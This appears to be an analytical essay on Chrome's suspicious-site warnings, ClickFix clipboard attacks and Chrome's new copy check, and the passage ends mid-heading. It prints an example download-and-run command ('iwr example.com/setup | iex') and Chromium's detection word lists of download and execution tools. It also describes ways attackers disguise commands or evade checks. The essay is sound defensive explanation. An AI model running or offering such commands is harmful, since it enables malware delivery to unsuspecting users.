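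Targeting warnings better may matter more than showing fewer of them. *Breaking Bad Email Habits* (2026) summarises a three-month experiment by Abbasi and colleagues with 1,218 employees, in which a model predicted how likely each person was to fall for a phishing site and those predictions guided the warnings. Employees who got these warnings made three to six times fewer transactions with phishing sites than the comparison groups. Chrome's two warning levels depend on how certain Google is about the site, and Google's description doesn't suggest that the threshold also depends on the user.

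### An honest shop with a countdown timer

Rijo raises the problem of landing pages that use urgency to sell. These pages may have countdown timers, boxes that imitate system messages, or download buttons that look like part of the operating system, all of which also appear on scam pages.

A small company might sell a useful program for recovering deleted photos. The program works, and the company gives refunds. But its page has a 15-minute countdown to the end of a discount and a grey button styled like a Windows dialog, and its domain is three weeks old.

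Gemini could help the shop, because the page names its own brand and openly offers a product. The domain's reputation can't help yet. The timer and the button reasonably count against the shop, since they are more common on scam pages than on the web as a whole. A careful reviewer with only this evidence might also call the page suspicious. A red warning page would be hard to defend, but a pop-up worded as a suspicion would be fairly accurate.

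It isn't clear that the pop-up would be a false positive. If the timer restarts for every visitor, the shop is deceiving its customers about the discount, though it isn't stealing from them. Google's definition covers deceptive patterns and only a *possible* risk of harm, so the warning can be correct for a page that never harms anyone. This makes the new level's precision hard to measure, because a researcher would first have to decide whether to count only warnings about scams as correct or to include warnings about pushy but legitimate pages.

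The shop's losses could be hard to notice. Suppose it has 2,000 visitors and 40 orders a day, 600 of the visitors use Enhanced Protection, and half of those leave when they see the pop-up. The shop loses about six orders a day, or 15% of its sales. Daily orders vary randomly by about that much, so the owner might take weeks to see a pattern. An owner who uses Standard Protection would not see the pop-up when opening the page.

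Google has labelled legitimate sites suspicious before. In 2019 it released a Chrome extension called Suspicious Site Reporter, which flagged sites that seemed doubtful. Search Engine Journal's *New Chrome Security Extension Flags Small Sites as Suspicious* found that it flagged any site outside the 5,000 most popular. It also flagged Walmart and Mozilla for a user who had not visited them in the previous three months. The extension was for volunteers and didn't block anything, so its mistakes did little harm. The 2026 warning uses much richer evidence, including the page's text when Gemini has read it, and should be far more accurate. But it can appear to more than a billion people, and a new or obscure domain is still likely to count against a site.

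Google already has a method that could protect shops with regular customers from mistaken warnings. Chrome has a separate warning for addresses that resemble a well-known site's, and Google admits that this warning sometimes flags harmless pages. To limit these mistakes, Chrome doesn't show it on sites that the user visits frequently. If the suspicious site warning followed the same rule, a shop's regular customers would never see it, and Chrome would miss few additional scams. Google has not announced such a rule.

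### Can a site owner appeal?

Rijo found no answer to this in Google's post. Google did not publish the threshold between the two levels, the list of deceptive patterns, or an estimate of how many more warnings Chrome would show. It also didn't explain how owners would learn that their pages were judged suspicious, or how to get a mistaken verdict reviewed. Google has good reason to keep the patterns and thresholds secret, because scammers would design pages to stay just below them. But that reason doesn't apply to telling an owner about a verdict that any visitor with Enhanced Protection can already see.

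*Dangerous/Deceptive Site Warning in Chrome*, by the web host 20i, directs owners of sites flagged as dangerous to Google's Safe Browsing status tool, where anyone can look up a site. Verified owners can also see security problems in Google Search Console, Google's service for people who run websites, and request a review there once they have fixed the cause.

This process may not cover the new level. Google's help page on unsafe sites has a heading for owners whose "site or software is marked dangerous or suspicious", but the heading was already there in September 2025, before Chrome had suspicious site warnings, so "suspicious" probably referred to software under the 2024 download levels. The status tool may also not show suspicious verdicts, because it reports what Google has found about a site, while a suspicious verdict may depend on a live check of one page during one visit. The owner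 of the photo-recovery shop could then look up the domain, find nothing against it, and still lose customers because of the pop-up.

The review process is also designed for sites that have something to repair, such as malware that a hacker has planted. The photo-recovery shop has no malware. Its owner could remove the timer and restyle the button, but without a list of the patterns, they would have to guess which one caused the warning.

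"Mark as safe" might give Google another way to discover mistakes, if thousands of visitors choose it on the same page. Reporters covering the feature did not establish whether Chrome sends these choices to Google. Spiegel, a Japanese blogger, welcomed the option but said it would be exploitative for Google to make users correct its errors and then collect the answers. These choices would also be an unreliable signal, since scammers could mark their own pages as safe and persuade victims to do the same.

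## ClickFix: how a web page gets people to run malware themselves

A ClickFix page gets people to paste a harmful command into a system window and run it, usually by presenting it as a fix for an invented error or as a way to prove they are human. Splunk's *Beyond The Click* points out that the attacker doesn't need to exploit a technical vulnerability. The browser, the clipboard (the temporary store for copied text) and the operating system all work as designed.

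ClickFix differs from an exploit, which uses a software flaw and may need nothing from the victim except a visit to a page. It also differs from ordinary phishing, where the victim gives away a password or card number, and from a malicious download, where the victim saves a harmful file and opens it. A fake browser update is a malicious download if the page offers an "update" file, and ClickFix if the page gives the visitor a command to paste.

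The phishing and ClickFix categories overlap. Many ClickFix attacks begin with a phishing email that links to the page, so one analyst may count an attack as phishing and another as ClickFix.

### An attack step by step

*Think before you Click(Fix)*, a Microsoft advisory (2025), describes attacks that begin when someone presses play on a website that streams pirated films. A new tab opens with what looks like a security check from Cloudflare, a company whose "verify you are human" box appears on many real sites. Other lures in the advisory imitate a browser crash, a Word document that won't open, and a Discord server's verification check for new members.

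When the visitor ticks the box, a spinner appears. On one page that Microsoft analyzed, the spinner was only an animation, and ticking the box made the page copy a command to the clipboard. The page used a standard browser function that ordinary websites use for their "copy" buttons. Push Security, which sells browser security, finds that the page copies the command automatically in nine out of ten cases.

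The page then shows "verification steps", typically pressing Windows+R, then Ctrl+V, then Enter. The first step opens the Run box, a Windows dialog for starting programs by name. The second pastes the command and the third runs it. This may look like an odd but harmless test to someone who has never used the Run box, and Microsoft believes the attackers rely on that unfamiliarity. Early lures sent people to PowerShell or Windows Terminal, which run typed commands. Microsoft suspects attackers moved to the Run box because a Windows warning about pasting several lines at once was putting victims off.

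The Run box accepts at most about 259 characters, which is too short for most malware, so the command usually uses a program already on the computer to fetch a longer script from the attacker's server and run it. The most common choice is PowerShell, which administrators use to manage Windows computers. Security researchers call such programs living-off-the-land binaries, or LOLBins, because attackers use them instead of bringing their own tools.

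ClickFix attacks most often deliver Lumma Stealer, according to Microsoft. It is an infostealer, malware that collects data such as saved passwords and sends it to the attacker. Other attacks install software that lets the attacker control the computer remotely.

Some attacks have many more stages. In a campaign Microsoft identified in May 2025, emails led people in Portuguese organisations to a fake tax authority site. The command they pasted fetched a script, which set up a second script, which downloaded a third. The third script looked for antivirus software and scheduled a restart, after which the computer was supposed to load Lampion, an infostealer aimed at banking information. Microsoft's investigators never received Lampion, because the attackers had disabled the line of code that downloaded it.

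### Why the copied command can differ from the one shown

A web page can copy text to the clipboard that differs from what it shows on screen. Legitimate sites do this routinely, as when a "copy link" button copies an address that appears nowhere on the page. A ClickFix page can show a harmless line of text and copy a harmful command, or copy the command without showing one.

The instructions a page shows don't always match the command it copies. In a 2025 campaign, a page imitating Spectrum, a US cable and internet company, copied one command to the clipboard for Windows visitors and another for Mac visitors. But it gave Mac users the Windows instructions, which would not have worked on their computers. Attackers have since become more careful, and Push Security describes a page that detects a Mac and shows Mac instructions.

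The victim could still notice the command after pasting it, so attackers disguise it. Many of the commands Microsoft collected include a fake confirmation such as "I am not a robot", followed by a verification number. The Run box is narrow and normally shows the end of a long line, so if the attacker puts the confirmation last, it may be all the victim sees. Attackers also encode commands, split up words that would reveal the command's purpose, or add reassuring phrases that mention Microsoft Defender, Windows' built-in antivirus program. Even someone who reads the whole line may not be able to tell what it does.

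In some early attacks, the command also removed itself from the clipboard, so a victim who became suspicious afterward could not paste it somewhere to inspect it. Investigators at Kroll found this behavior in code from ClearFake, a group of attacks that used fake browser errors. However, Windows keeps a history of commands successfully run from the Run box, which investigators can check.

### Why download checks and some security software miss it

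Chrome's download checks, including the deep scans in Enhanced Protection, examine files that Chrome downloads. In a ClickFix attack, Chrome loads a web page and passes a text command to the clipboard. PowerShell or another tool then fetches the malware outside the browser, so Chrome has no file to scan. Chrome's new check runs when the page copies the command, which is the last point at which Chrome can easily step in.

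Email filters have a similar problem, because the message may contain only a link. In June 2025, attackers sent emails about a supposed problem with the recipient's US Social Security statement. The button in the email led first to a Google Ads address, which redirected to the fake site. This helped the message get past filters, and recipients who followed the usual advice to hover over a link before clicking would have seen only the Google address.

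Antivirus programs have traditionally looked for harmful files on the disk. ClickFix malware often runs only in the computer's memory, sometimes inside a legitimate Windows program, so there may be no such file to find. Security software also can't block PowerShell everywhere, since administrators need it. Because the user started the command, the first step can look like ordinary work.

Macs put a quarantine mark on downloaded files so that the system checks them before they open. The Mac command in the fake Spectrum campaign kept prompting for the user's password until the user entered the correct one. It then ran the malware after using the password to remove the mark.

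Software that examines commands and scripts as they run has a better chance of catching the attack. Windows lets antivirus programs inspect PowerShell scripts when they run, even if the attacker disguised the original command. But in early 2025, Microsoft was still seeing people run ClickFix commands on thousands of devices a month, even though those devices had endpoint detection software, which watches for suspicious behaviour.

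Microsoft responded by collecting commands from the Run box histories of affected computers, extracting the addresses they contacted, and blocking those addresses. If the computer can't reach the attacker's server, the command can't download the malware. This is a sensible defence, though Microsoft sells the product that does the blocking and its advisory gives no success rate. Microsoft also suggests that organisations remove the Run box for staff who don't need it. That would stop the most common version of the attack, but not one that sends people to PowerShell or Terminal.

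### From fake Word errors to CrashFix

The first reports of ClickFix date from 2024. According to the US Department of Health and Human Services (HHS, 2024), a criminal group known as TA571 sent phishing emails in March 2024 with attachments that looked like Word documents. The attachments showed a fake error with instructions to run PowerShell code to fix it. By May, ClearFake's operators were using a similar trick on legitimate websites they had hacked.

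Proofpoint's *From Clipboard to Compromise* brought these attacks to wider attention in June 2024. Proofpoint's researchers noted that the victim had to do a lot of the work, but thought the trick could succeed because it presented a believable problem and its solution together. WaterISAC's *Threat Awareness*, an alert for water utilities based on Proofpoint's findings, used "ClickFix" for one of several groups of attacks, not yet for the technique as a whole.

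HHS issued its alert to the health sector in October 2024, and Microsoft dates the surge in ClickFix to November. From late 2024, criminals could buy ready-made kits on hacker forums for $200 to $1,500 a month. A buyer could choose a language and a Cloudflare or Google Meet design, and the kit would produce both the page and the command. The sellers, who had reason to exaggerate, also promised that their kits would get past antivirus software.

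The attackers also moved from attachments to links, and a group that Microsoft tracks as Storm-0249 switched from email to hacked websites in March 2025. A visitor to one of these sites briefly saw the real page before a fake Cloudflare check replaced it. Checking the address would not have helped, because it was the site's correct address. A domain's good reputation is also weaker evidence of safety in such a case.

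By April 2025, Proofpoint was reporting that state-sponsored hackers had also tried the technique. The Mac version followed within weeks. The Center for Internet Security's *ClickFix* (2025) attributes the technique's spread that year partly to its ability to target several operating systems. An attacker needs a different command for each system but can reuse most of the page.

Later variants made the supposed problem more convincing. Arete's *Click-Fix Attacks Now Using Fake Blue Screen of Death* describes a campaign that targeted the hospitality sector with a fake human-verification check and an imitation of the blue screen Windows shows when it crashes.

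In CrashFix, which the security company Huntress described in January 2026, a malicious browser extension crashes the browser and then offers a repair that is itself a ClickFix attack. Most ClickFix lures describe a problem that doesn't exist, so a sceptical person can close the tab and find that everything works. CrashFix really does break the browser, and closing the page doesn't fix it because the extension is still installed.

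The Mac attacks have also become harder for investigators to find. In August, Microsoft (2026) described a campaign that generated its domain names in bulk and had recently added cloaking, which can hide the lure from security companies' crawlers.

ClickFix was still in heavy use that autumn. The *Digital Defense Report 2026* (Microsoft, 2026) lists it with phishing and impersonation as one of the ways attackers continue to exploit people's behaviour.

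### How common is ClickFix?

CNews cites the Russian security company Informzashchita as saying that ClickFix accounted for 47% of initial break-ins in 2025. The number almost certainly comes from the previous year's edition of the same Microsoft report, which gives exactly that share, but of a much narrower category than all break-ins (Microsoft, 2025).

| Who counted | What they counted | Period | ClickFix share |
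|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Defender Experts | Attacks in the team's notifications to customers | Probably July 2024 to June 2025 | 47% |
| Microsoft Incident Response | Breaches that the team investigated | Microsoft's 2025 financial year | No separate figure |
| ESET | Attacks that its software blocked | December 2024 to May 2025 | Nearly 8% |

In the Defender Experts service, Microsoft's analysts look for attackers in the networks of paying organisations. Phishing came second in their notifications at 35%, and software vulnerabilities made up only 1%. The listed methods add up to 100% with no entry for unknown causes, so Microsoft may have left out attacks whose starting point it could not identify. The period is probably not calendar 2025, since the 2026 edition (Microsoft, 2026) defines the 2025 reporting period as July 2024 to June 2025.

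The Incident Response team's figures look very different. Social engineering accounted for 10% of its cases, phishing for 6%, and drive-by compromise, in which a visit to a website starts the attack, for 4%. Even if all those cases were ClickFix, they would make up only 20% of the team's cases. Attacks on public-facing applications made up 11%, compared with 1% for all vulnerabilities in the Defender Experts data. The two teams evidently see different kinds of attack, and neither sees a random sample.

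The incident figures could still understate ClickFix's role. The team could not determine how the intrusion began in a fifth of its cases, and in another 11% the intruder used a valid account. Criminals often get passwords for such accounts from infostealers, the malware ClickFix most often installs. If an employee falls for a fake human check in March and a criminal uses the stolen password in June, investigators may record only the June login.

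The antivirus maker ESET (2025) ranked ClickFix as the second most common attack method after phishing. Its detections of what it calls ClickFix/FakeCaptcha rose by 517%, or about sixfold, from one half-year to the next. If the total number of blocked attacks stayed the same, ClickFix's share in the earlier half-year was about 1.3%. ESET's figure is probably the better guide for ordinary Chrome users, because its customers include households. But ESET counts blocked attempts, and many of the people targeted would never have pasted the command.

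It is unclear from the 2026 figures whether ClickFix is still growing. Phishing rose from 7% to 23% of the intrusions that Microsoft's incident responders investigated, according to Help Net Security's *AI is giving attackers a head start, Microsoft warns* (2026). Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft* adds that social engineering fell from 15% to 7%. This could mean that ClickFix declined, or that Microsoft now counts some of it under another heading. Microsoft has probably changed its method, because the 2025 edition of its report gave 10% rather than 15% for what seems to be the same year.

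InfoCom's *Η AI επιταχύνει τις κυβερνοεπιθέσεις και αυξάνει την πίεση στις επιχειρήσεις* (2026) quotes a broader figure from the 2026 report, that 73.3% of attempts to gain initial access involved user execution, valid accounts, social engineering or phishing. "User execution" means that the victim runs something harmful. That would include ClickFix, but also opening an infected attachment, so the figure is weak evidence of how common ClickFix is.

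### How many people run the command?

Microsoft's advisory allows only a very rough estimate of how often ClickFix succeeds. It reports that campaigns were targeting thousands of devices a day, and that in early 2025 users ran the command on thousands of devices a month. If both figures were 3,000, users would have run the command on about 3% of targeted devices. But "thousands" could mean 2,000 or 9,000, so the rate could be anywhere from under 1% to 15%. The two figures may also cover different groups of devices, since the first includes home users and the second comes from the Defender Experts team.

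Push Security notes that security training has spent at least a decade warning people about suspicious links, risky files and fake login pages, but not about opening a program and running a command. Someone who has learned those lessons could still follow the instructions on a fake human check. The simple rule that a real human check never requires pasting anything into a system window would cover most cases.

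A low success rate is enough for attackers. In the film-streaming campaign of April 2025, malicious adverts could send tens of thousands, possibly hundreds of thousands, of people to scam pages in a single day. If 50,000 of them reached a ClickFix page and 1 in 500 ran the command, the attacker would infect 100 computers that day, using a kit that costs at most $1,500 a month.

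## How Chrome checks copied commands

ClickFix gets past Chrome's download checks because the browser handles only text, so Google's new check examines that text. Help Net Security reports that when someone with Enhanced Protection copies a suspicious command, Chrome removes personally identifiable information from it, sends the rest to Safe Browsing, and shows a warning if Safe Browsing classifies the command as dangerous.

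Google hasn't explained what makes a command suspicious, how Chrome recognises personal information, how long the check takes, or whether the command stays on the clipboard. Chromium's source code shows some of this, but the most detailed version is from before the launch, so the finished check may differ.

| Step | What Google has said | What the pre-launch code shows |
|---|---|---|
| Someone copies text | Enhanced Protection must be on | One check per page address, for text of up to 1,000 characters |
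| Chrome tests the text on the device | Chrome picks out suspicious commands | The test needs a download tool, an address and a way to run code |
| Chrome removes personal information | This happens before Chrome sends the text | No such step in the file that builds the report |
| Safe Browsing reaches a verdict | It analyses the text | Nothing, because this happens on Google's servers |
| Chrome warns the user | A warning appears if the command is dangerous | A full-page warning, with the text still on the clipboard |

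### From the copy to the warning

In the pre-launch code, Chromium first applies a length limit, 1,000 characters by default. Every command that fits in the Windows Run box is well below that, but a long command meant for PowerShell or a Mac's Terminal could exceed it. According to a comment in Chromium, the trigger is a page's use of the browser's copy function, but Google refers to users copying commands, so it is unclear whether selecting a command by hand and pressing Ctrl+C also triggers the check.

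Chrome then decides whether to examine the page. It skips Incognito tabs, pages on private networks and addresses that an employer has exempted. It also skips sites on a Google allowlist. This avoids many needless checks on well-known sites, but a hacked site on the list would also go unchecked.

Google can also choose what share of the remaining copies Chrome checks. In Chromium's default settings, the share is zero and the feature is off, so Google would have to switch it on remotely. If the share were 50%, Chrome would miss at least half of all ClickFix commands even if the rest of the system worked perfectly. Google hasn't published the live setting.

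After the on-device test, Chrome sends its report and waits for a verdict. If the verdict is bad, Chrome's code replaces the page with a full-page warning. Punto Informatico describes it as the red warning and says it appears almost in real time, though Google has published no timings.

Chrome probably has a few seconds to warn the visitor, who must still follow the page's instructions after the command reaches the clipboard. A server can usually answer in that time, but Chrome's code can do other work before it sends the report, such as computing a numerical summary of the page's appearance, and a slow connection adds more delay. If the tab moves to another page before the answer arrives, Chrome drops the warning.

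Chrome starts the check after the text has reached the clipboard, and nothing in the file that handles the check clears the clipboard. Someone who already has the Run box open can still paste the command and run it while the red page is on the screen. The page covers the scammer's instructions and contradicts them, which should be enough for most people, but clearing the clipboard as well would protect someone who presses the keys without stopping to think.

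### What the test on the device looks for

ClickFix commands usually download something and run it, and the pre-launch test is a simple search for that pattern. Chrome splits the copied text into words and compares them with several lists. By default, the listed download tools are `curl`, `wget` and PowerShell's `Invoke-WebRequest`, or `iwr`. The list of commands that can run code includes `bash`, `cmd` and PowerShell's `Invoke-Expression`, or `iex`. Chrome marks the text as suspicious if it contains a download tool, a web address and a command that can run code.

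The command `iwr example.com/setup | iex` has all three because it downloads a script from an address and immediately runs it. The command `curl example.com/photo.jpg` only downloads a picture, so Chrome would not mark it. Some tools count as two of the three. The Windows program `mshta` can both download and run a script, so `mshta` and an address are enough. A decoding tool such as `base64` counts as both the download tool and the address, because the encoded text might hide them.

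This is a sensible first filter, and it takes little enough computing power to run on any computer. But a fixed list of words can easily miss things. The default lists don't include "PowerShell", so an encoded PowerShell command might contain no listed word. Google can change the lists remotely, and it had good reason to do so before the launch, since its own announcement lists PowerShell as a typical ClickFix tool.

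The design was still changing. An earlier version of Chromium had the copy trigger and the length limits but no settings for analysing the text. The next version added the word lists. In that version, Chrome would have reported the page to Safe Browsing whether or not the text looked suspicious. The test only affected how much detail about the copied text the report included.

A later version of Chromium adds a "suspicious token filter", which probably stops Chrome from reporting text that contains none of the listed words. This would fit Google's public description better. The filter might also close a gap in the earlier code, where Chrome checked only one copy per page address, so a page could use up the check by copying a harmless sentence and then copy the command. The later version also adds a priority system for triggers. Before that, a new trigger on the same page could cancel a check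 that was still at an early stage.

### Whether Gemini reads the command

Help Net Security says that Chrome sends the copied command to Safe Browsing, and mentions Gemini only in connection with the page check. No source says that Gemini evaluates copied commands.

Chromium's code connects the two features in a different way. When the browser sends any report of this kind, including one triggered by a copy, it can also start a Gemini scam check. That call passes the page's address and the type of trigger, but not the copied text. The switch for it was off by default, and its name suggests that Google was using it to collect measurements. A suspicious copy may therefore lead Gemini to look at the page, which would be useful because a fake human check is easier to recognise from its instructions than from its command. Safe Browsing could still use another AI model on the command itself, but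 Google hasn't said that it does.

### Why the moment of copying matters

Browsers have dealt with harmful pasting before. In the text/plain blog post *Attack Techniques* (2024, later updated), Eric Lawrence of Microsoft Defender recalls a wave of attacks around 2011 in which people pasted code into the browser's address bar and lost control of their Facebook accounts. Browsers began removing the `javascript:` prefix from pasted text so that the code wouldn't run. Chrome and Firefox now also block pasting into their developer tools by default.

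In those attacks, the browser controlled where the victim pasted the text. A ClickFix victim pastes it into the Run box or Terminal, which Chrome doesn't control, so copying is the last step Chrome can detect. Push Security points out that the copying happens inside the browser's sandbox (the barrier that separates web pages from the rest of the computer), so typical security tools can't detect the attack until the victim tries to run the command.

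Security analysts had asked Google for a similar check before the launch. In *Click-fix*, a thread on a Chromium mailing list, Walton (2025) suggested showing a notice whenever a page changes the clipboard, as the browser extension Malwarebytes Browser Guard already did. Nathan Parker replied for Chromium eight days later that the team knew of the attack and was looking for better ways to detect and flag pages that use it. Google announced the finished check 21 months after Walton's message.

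Showing a notice every time a page changes the clipboard would be much simpler than Google's design, and disguising the command could not prevent the notice. But the notice would also appear whenever someone used an ordinary "copy link" button, so people would soon learn to ignore it. A ClickFix page could also tell them that the notice was part of the verification.

People who never copy commands from web pages may benefit most from Google's check. Most ClickFix pages put the command on the clipboard themselves, and a person who has never used PowerShell is unlikely to notice anything odd about it. Clubic's *Chrome détecte les arnaques ClickFix que des arnaqueurs vous font copier* argues that people who never copy commands will gain little from the check, but this seems wrong.

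### A developer copying an installer

Many software projects tell users to install a program by pasting one line into PowerShell or Terminal. The line downloads an installation script and runs it, just as a ClickFix command does. `iwr example.com/setup | iex` could come from a software project's page or a ClickFix page, and the test on the device can't distinguish between them.

Clubic warns that a legitimate PowerShell command may go to Google for analysis. It reports Google's reply that the check will be very precise so as not to disturb developers. TecnoAndroid's *Google Chrome contro le truffe* likewise says Google designed the system to stay out of developers' way. That promise concerns false warnings, so Chrome may still send legitimate commands to Google.

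Safe Browsing has better evidence than the command's wording, such as the age and history of the installation address. A command is probably fine if thousands of people have used the same address for three years without trouble, and almost certainly isn't if the address is two days old and the page is presented as a human check. A new open-source project with a week-old website and few users is harder to judge. A mistaken red page wouldn't stop an experienced developer from installing the program, because the command would still be on the clipboard, but it could scare others away from the project.

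High precision lowers recall, so more harmful commands get no warning. In an invented example, Enhanced Protection users copy a million download-and-run commands a day, of which 20,000 are ClickFix.

| Threshold for a warning | ClickFix commands caught | Legitimate commands flagged | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Strict | 12,000 | 100 | 99% | 60% |
| Loose | 18,000 | 9,800 | 65% | 90% |

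With the strict threshold, developers would hardly ever see a false warning, but 8,000 people a day would get no warning about a harmful command. Better evidence can improve both precision and recall. Without it, Google has to choose between them, and its promise to developers suggests that it favors a stricter threshold. Google hasn't published figures for precision or recall.

Google could warn about some of the uncertain commands with the milder pop-up it now uses for suspicious sites. It has not announced a milder warning for commands.

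Developers could also reach the limit on reports. By default, Chromium allows an Enhanced Protection user ten reports a day, and the copy check shares this allowance with other page checks. In the version that reported every eligible copy, a developer who copied snippets from ten unfamiliar pages would have had no reports left that day for a ClickFix page. The later filter should make this much rarer.

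### A command the victim types

A page that asks visitors to type a command avoids the copy check, because nothing reaches the clipboard. The same is true when a fake technician dictates the command over the phone.

Attackers could avoid the copy check by asking victims to type the command, but this would work less often. Few people will type 200 characters of encoded text correctly, and the length alone may make them suspicious. An attacker would need a short command, perhaps the name of a Windows program followed by a brief web address, which takes only about 20 characters. Even then, each extra step gives the victim time to reconsider, and one typing error can make the attack fail. If the copy check works well, some attackers will probably use this method anyway.

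Chrome's checks of the page itself still apply.

### A command that fetches the harmful part later

The copied command often contains nothing harmful except the address of the attacker's script. The test on the device can still flag it, because it looks for commands that download and run something. The check is harder for Safe Browsing, whose verdict depends on what is at the address.

IlSoftware.it's *Chrome controlla gli appunti per bloccare potenziali comandi pericolosi* calls the work on Google's servers a behavioural analysis. This could mean that Google downloads the script and runs it in an isolated environment, or that it only considers what the command would do. If Google downloads the script, the attacker can try cloaking again by sending Google a harmless script and the victim the real one. The attacker can also leave a harmless script at the address and replace it an hour later.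 Safe Browsing then has to rely on circumstantial evidence, such as the age of the address and the page's claims.

Other commands might not look like downloads. Software developers can install a package (ready-made code) by typing an installation command and the package's name. An attacker could publish a harmful package and ask people to install it this way, and the copied command would contain no web address or default download tool. This would mainly threaten developers, since most home users don't have the necessary software. Developers are also the group Google is trying hardest not to disturb.

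Attackers are already moving away from the standard PowerShell command. SiliconANGLE's *ClickFix moves into the browser and onto WebDAV, Cisco Talos finds* (2026) describes two campaigns that Cisco's threat researchers reported in September. One works in the browser without involving the operating system. The other uses WebDAV, which lets Windows open files on a web server much as if they were in a shared folder. A command that opens a program from such a folder may not need `curl` or any other listed download tool. Google can add new words and patterns to the test, but only after someone notices a new method.

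### Opera's Paste Protect and warnings on pasting

Opera introduced a similar protection before Chrome. According to Clubic, its Paste Protect feature has blocked the copying of suspicious commands since July, using rules built into the browser. Blocking is safer than Chrome's warnings if the rules are right, because a victim who ignores warnings still has nothing to paste. But it is more annoying for developers if the rules block a harmless command they need to copy.

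The security company Eye Security built a simple version of the same idea, a script that intercepts the browser's copy function and copies nothing if the text contains a word such as `mshta` or `powershell`. This would stop many ClickFix pages, but it would also block the copy button on a PowerShell tutorial. Opera presumably uses more careful rules, but rules that work entirely inside the browser can't use what Google knows about a two-day-old address, and attackers can test their commands against them in private. However, the browser can apply these rules without sending the command anywhere or waiting for an answer.

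Operating systems can step in when the user pastes. Apple added a prompt on pasting into Terminal in macOS 26.4, in March 2026, according to text/plain. Windows Terminal warns about pasted text that contains a line break, which can make a command run before the user presses Enter. A command on a single line doesn't trigger that warning. Lawrence describes no paste warning for the Run box.

| Where the protection acts | What it can see that the others can't | What it misses |
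|---|---|---|
| Chrome's copy check | The page and the command together with Google's data on other sites | Typed commands, and text copied in other programs |
| Opera's Paste Protect | The copy before it happens, so it can prevent it | Typed commands, and anything its rules don't cover |
| Paste prompt in a terminal | That someone is about to put the text into a command window, whatever program it came from | Typed commands, and the page's false story |
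| Security software on the computer | What the command does and what it downloads, even if the victim typed it | The chance to act before the command starts |

A paste prompt works with any browser, and with commands that arrive by email or chat. But Lawrence puts the harmless share of pasting at 99.99% and doubts that people would put up with a warning each time. Attackers can also switch to a program that has no prompt, as they seem to have done when they moved from PowerShell and Windows Terminal to the Run box. Adding a prompt to the Run box might not be enough either, because File Explorer's address bar can also run commands, and Lawrence mentions a real campaign that used the similar bar in the file-selection window.

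Windows could use information already on the clipboard to make its warnings more selective. When someone copies text from a web page, Chrome and other Chromium browsers add the page's address to the clipboard as a hidden label, and Firefox does something similar. The Run box could read this label and require confirmation only when the text came from the web. This would warn people following a fake human check just before they press Enter, without interrupting administrators who paste their own commands from a text file.

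## What Chrome sends to Google and what Google promises about it

Both the Gemini check and the copy check can send text from a web page to Google. Chrome can inspect the text on the device and send it to Google, and Google can store it and train AI models on it. Press reports often confused these four actions. Inspection on the device reveals nothing to Google by itself. Sending the text exposes it to Google's systems while they check it. If Google also stores the text, an employee, a court or a thief might get hold of it months later. A model trained on the text may retain traces of it after Google deletes the original.

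### What each mode sends

Chrome sends page addresses far more often than page text or copied commands. In Standard Protection, it first checks the address against a list of safe sites stored on the device. If the site isn't there, Chrome sends the first part of a hash of the address to Google through another company's server, which hides the user's IP address (the number that identifies an internet connection). Google's *How Chrome Safe Browsing keeps your browsing data private* says neither company can connect a real page address with an IP address.

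Enhanced Protection sends the full address, which can reveal a lot, as in the invented example `clinic.example/book/hiv-test`. Google's *Choose your Safe Browsing protection level in Chrome* says this happens when someone visits a site, but the other help page limits it to sites that Chrome has no information about. Google's *Enhanced Protection* (2022) supports the narrower version, since it describes real-time checks of "uncommon" sites. Chrome therefore probably sends nothing when someone visits a major newspaper, but sends the whole address when they visit a small clinic's booking page.

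Enhanced Protection also sends a small sample of page content, along with information about browser extensions and the computer. It already sent such samples before the Gemini check existed, and they are separate from the page text that Gemini reads.

Under Standard Protection, too, Chrome can send the full address and parts of the page directly to Google if a site behaves suspiciously or someone enters a saved password on an unfamiliar site.

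| Data | Inspected on the device | Sent in Enhanced Protection | Stored by Google | Used to train models | Sent in Standard Protection |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Page address | Yes | In full, for less common sites | For "a short period" | No specific promise | Hash prefix; sometimes in full after suspicious behaviour |
| Sample of page content | Yes | Yes | For "a short period" | No specific promise | Only after suspicious behaviour |
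| Page text for Gemini | Yes | Only with strong signs of a scam | Never, according to Google | Never, according to Google | No |
| Copied command | Yes | Only if suspicious, without personal information | No specific promise | No specific promise | No |

Even where Google makes no specific promise, its help pages limit the use of all Safe Browsing data to security. That would rule out using an address to choose advertisements, but it doesn't clearly rule out training a model to recognise scams, which is a security purpose.

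### The missing promise about copied commands

Clubic noticed that Google's promise never to log, keep or train on content appears in the part of its post about page text. About the clipboard, Google writes only that Chrome removes personal information before sending anything.

Other accounts of the post mostly support this reading. Help Net Security, Infobae and mobiFlip's *Google Chrome verbessert Schutz vor Phishing und Online-Betrug* all divide the promises in the same way. ETV Bharat is less clear, because it applies the promise to "any content sent off the device", which could include commands. But that phrase appears in its section on Gemini, just after a sentence about page text, and Gangwar limits the promise to data Chrome sends for Gemini's analysis, so Clubic is probably right.

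None of this is evidence that Google keeps the commands. It may delete them as quickly as it deletes page text but not have said so. Until Google says how long it keeps them, the best guide is its general promise from 2022 to keep Enhanced Protection data only "for a short period of time". That is weaker than a promise never to keep the data, and "short" could mean an hour or several months.

Google may also link the data to a user's Google Account. When it launched the mode in 2020, it said it would do this temporarily for signed-in users and anonymise the data after a short period. The link allows an attack on someone's Gmail to prompt stricter checks in their browser. The current help page still describes saving Safe Browsing data to the account but doesn't repeat the time limit. Google hasn't said whether the saved data includes copied commands.

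Google has a good reason to keep harmful commands, because they contain the addresses of attackers' servers. Harmless commands are much less useful, though they could help Google measure its false positives. If Google promised to delete every command that Safe Browsing clears, it would protect developers and lose little useful data.

Google has promised to remove personal information from copied commands but not from page text, which may include a signed-in visitor's name or email address. This omission matters less if Google does discard the text after the check.

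Some reports changed the promises in small but important ways. mobiFlip wrote that Google doesn't store page content permanently, wording that would allow Google to keep the text for a month. Punto Informatico wrote that Chrome removes "sensitive data" from commands, a broader category than personally identifiable information because it includes passwords even when they don't identify anyone.

Google's help pages seem not to have explained right away that the copy check could send Google a command the user had copied. Infobae's article on the October announcement summarised the Chrome help page as saying that Enhanced Protection sends the page address, the sample of page content, extension activity and system information. The summary didn't mention copied text. An older version of Google's *Manage Enhanced Safe Browsing for your account*, which covers the setting for a whole Google Account,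 doesn't list copied text either.

### Does Chrome read everything people copy?

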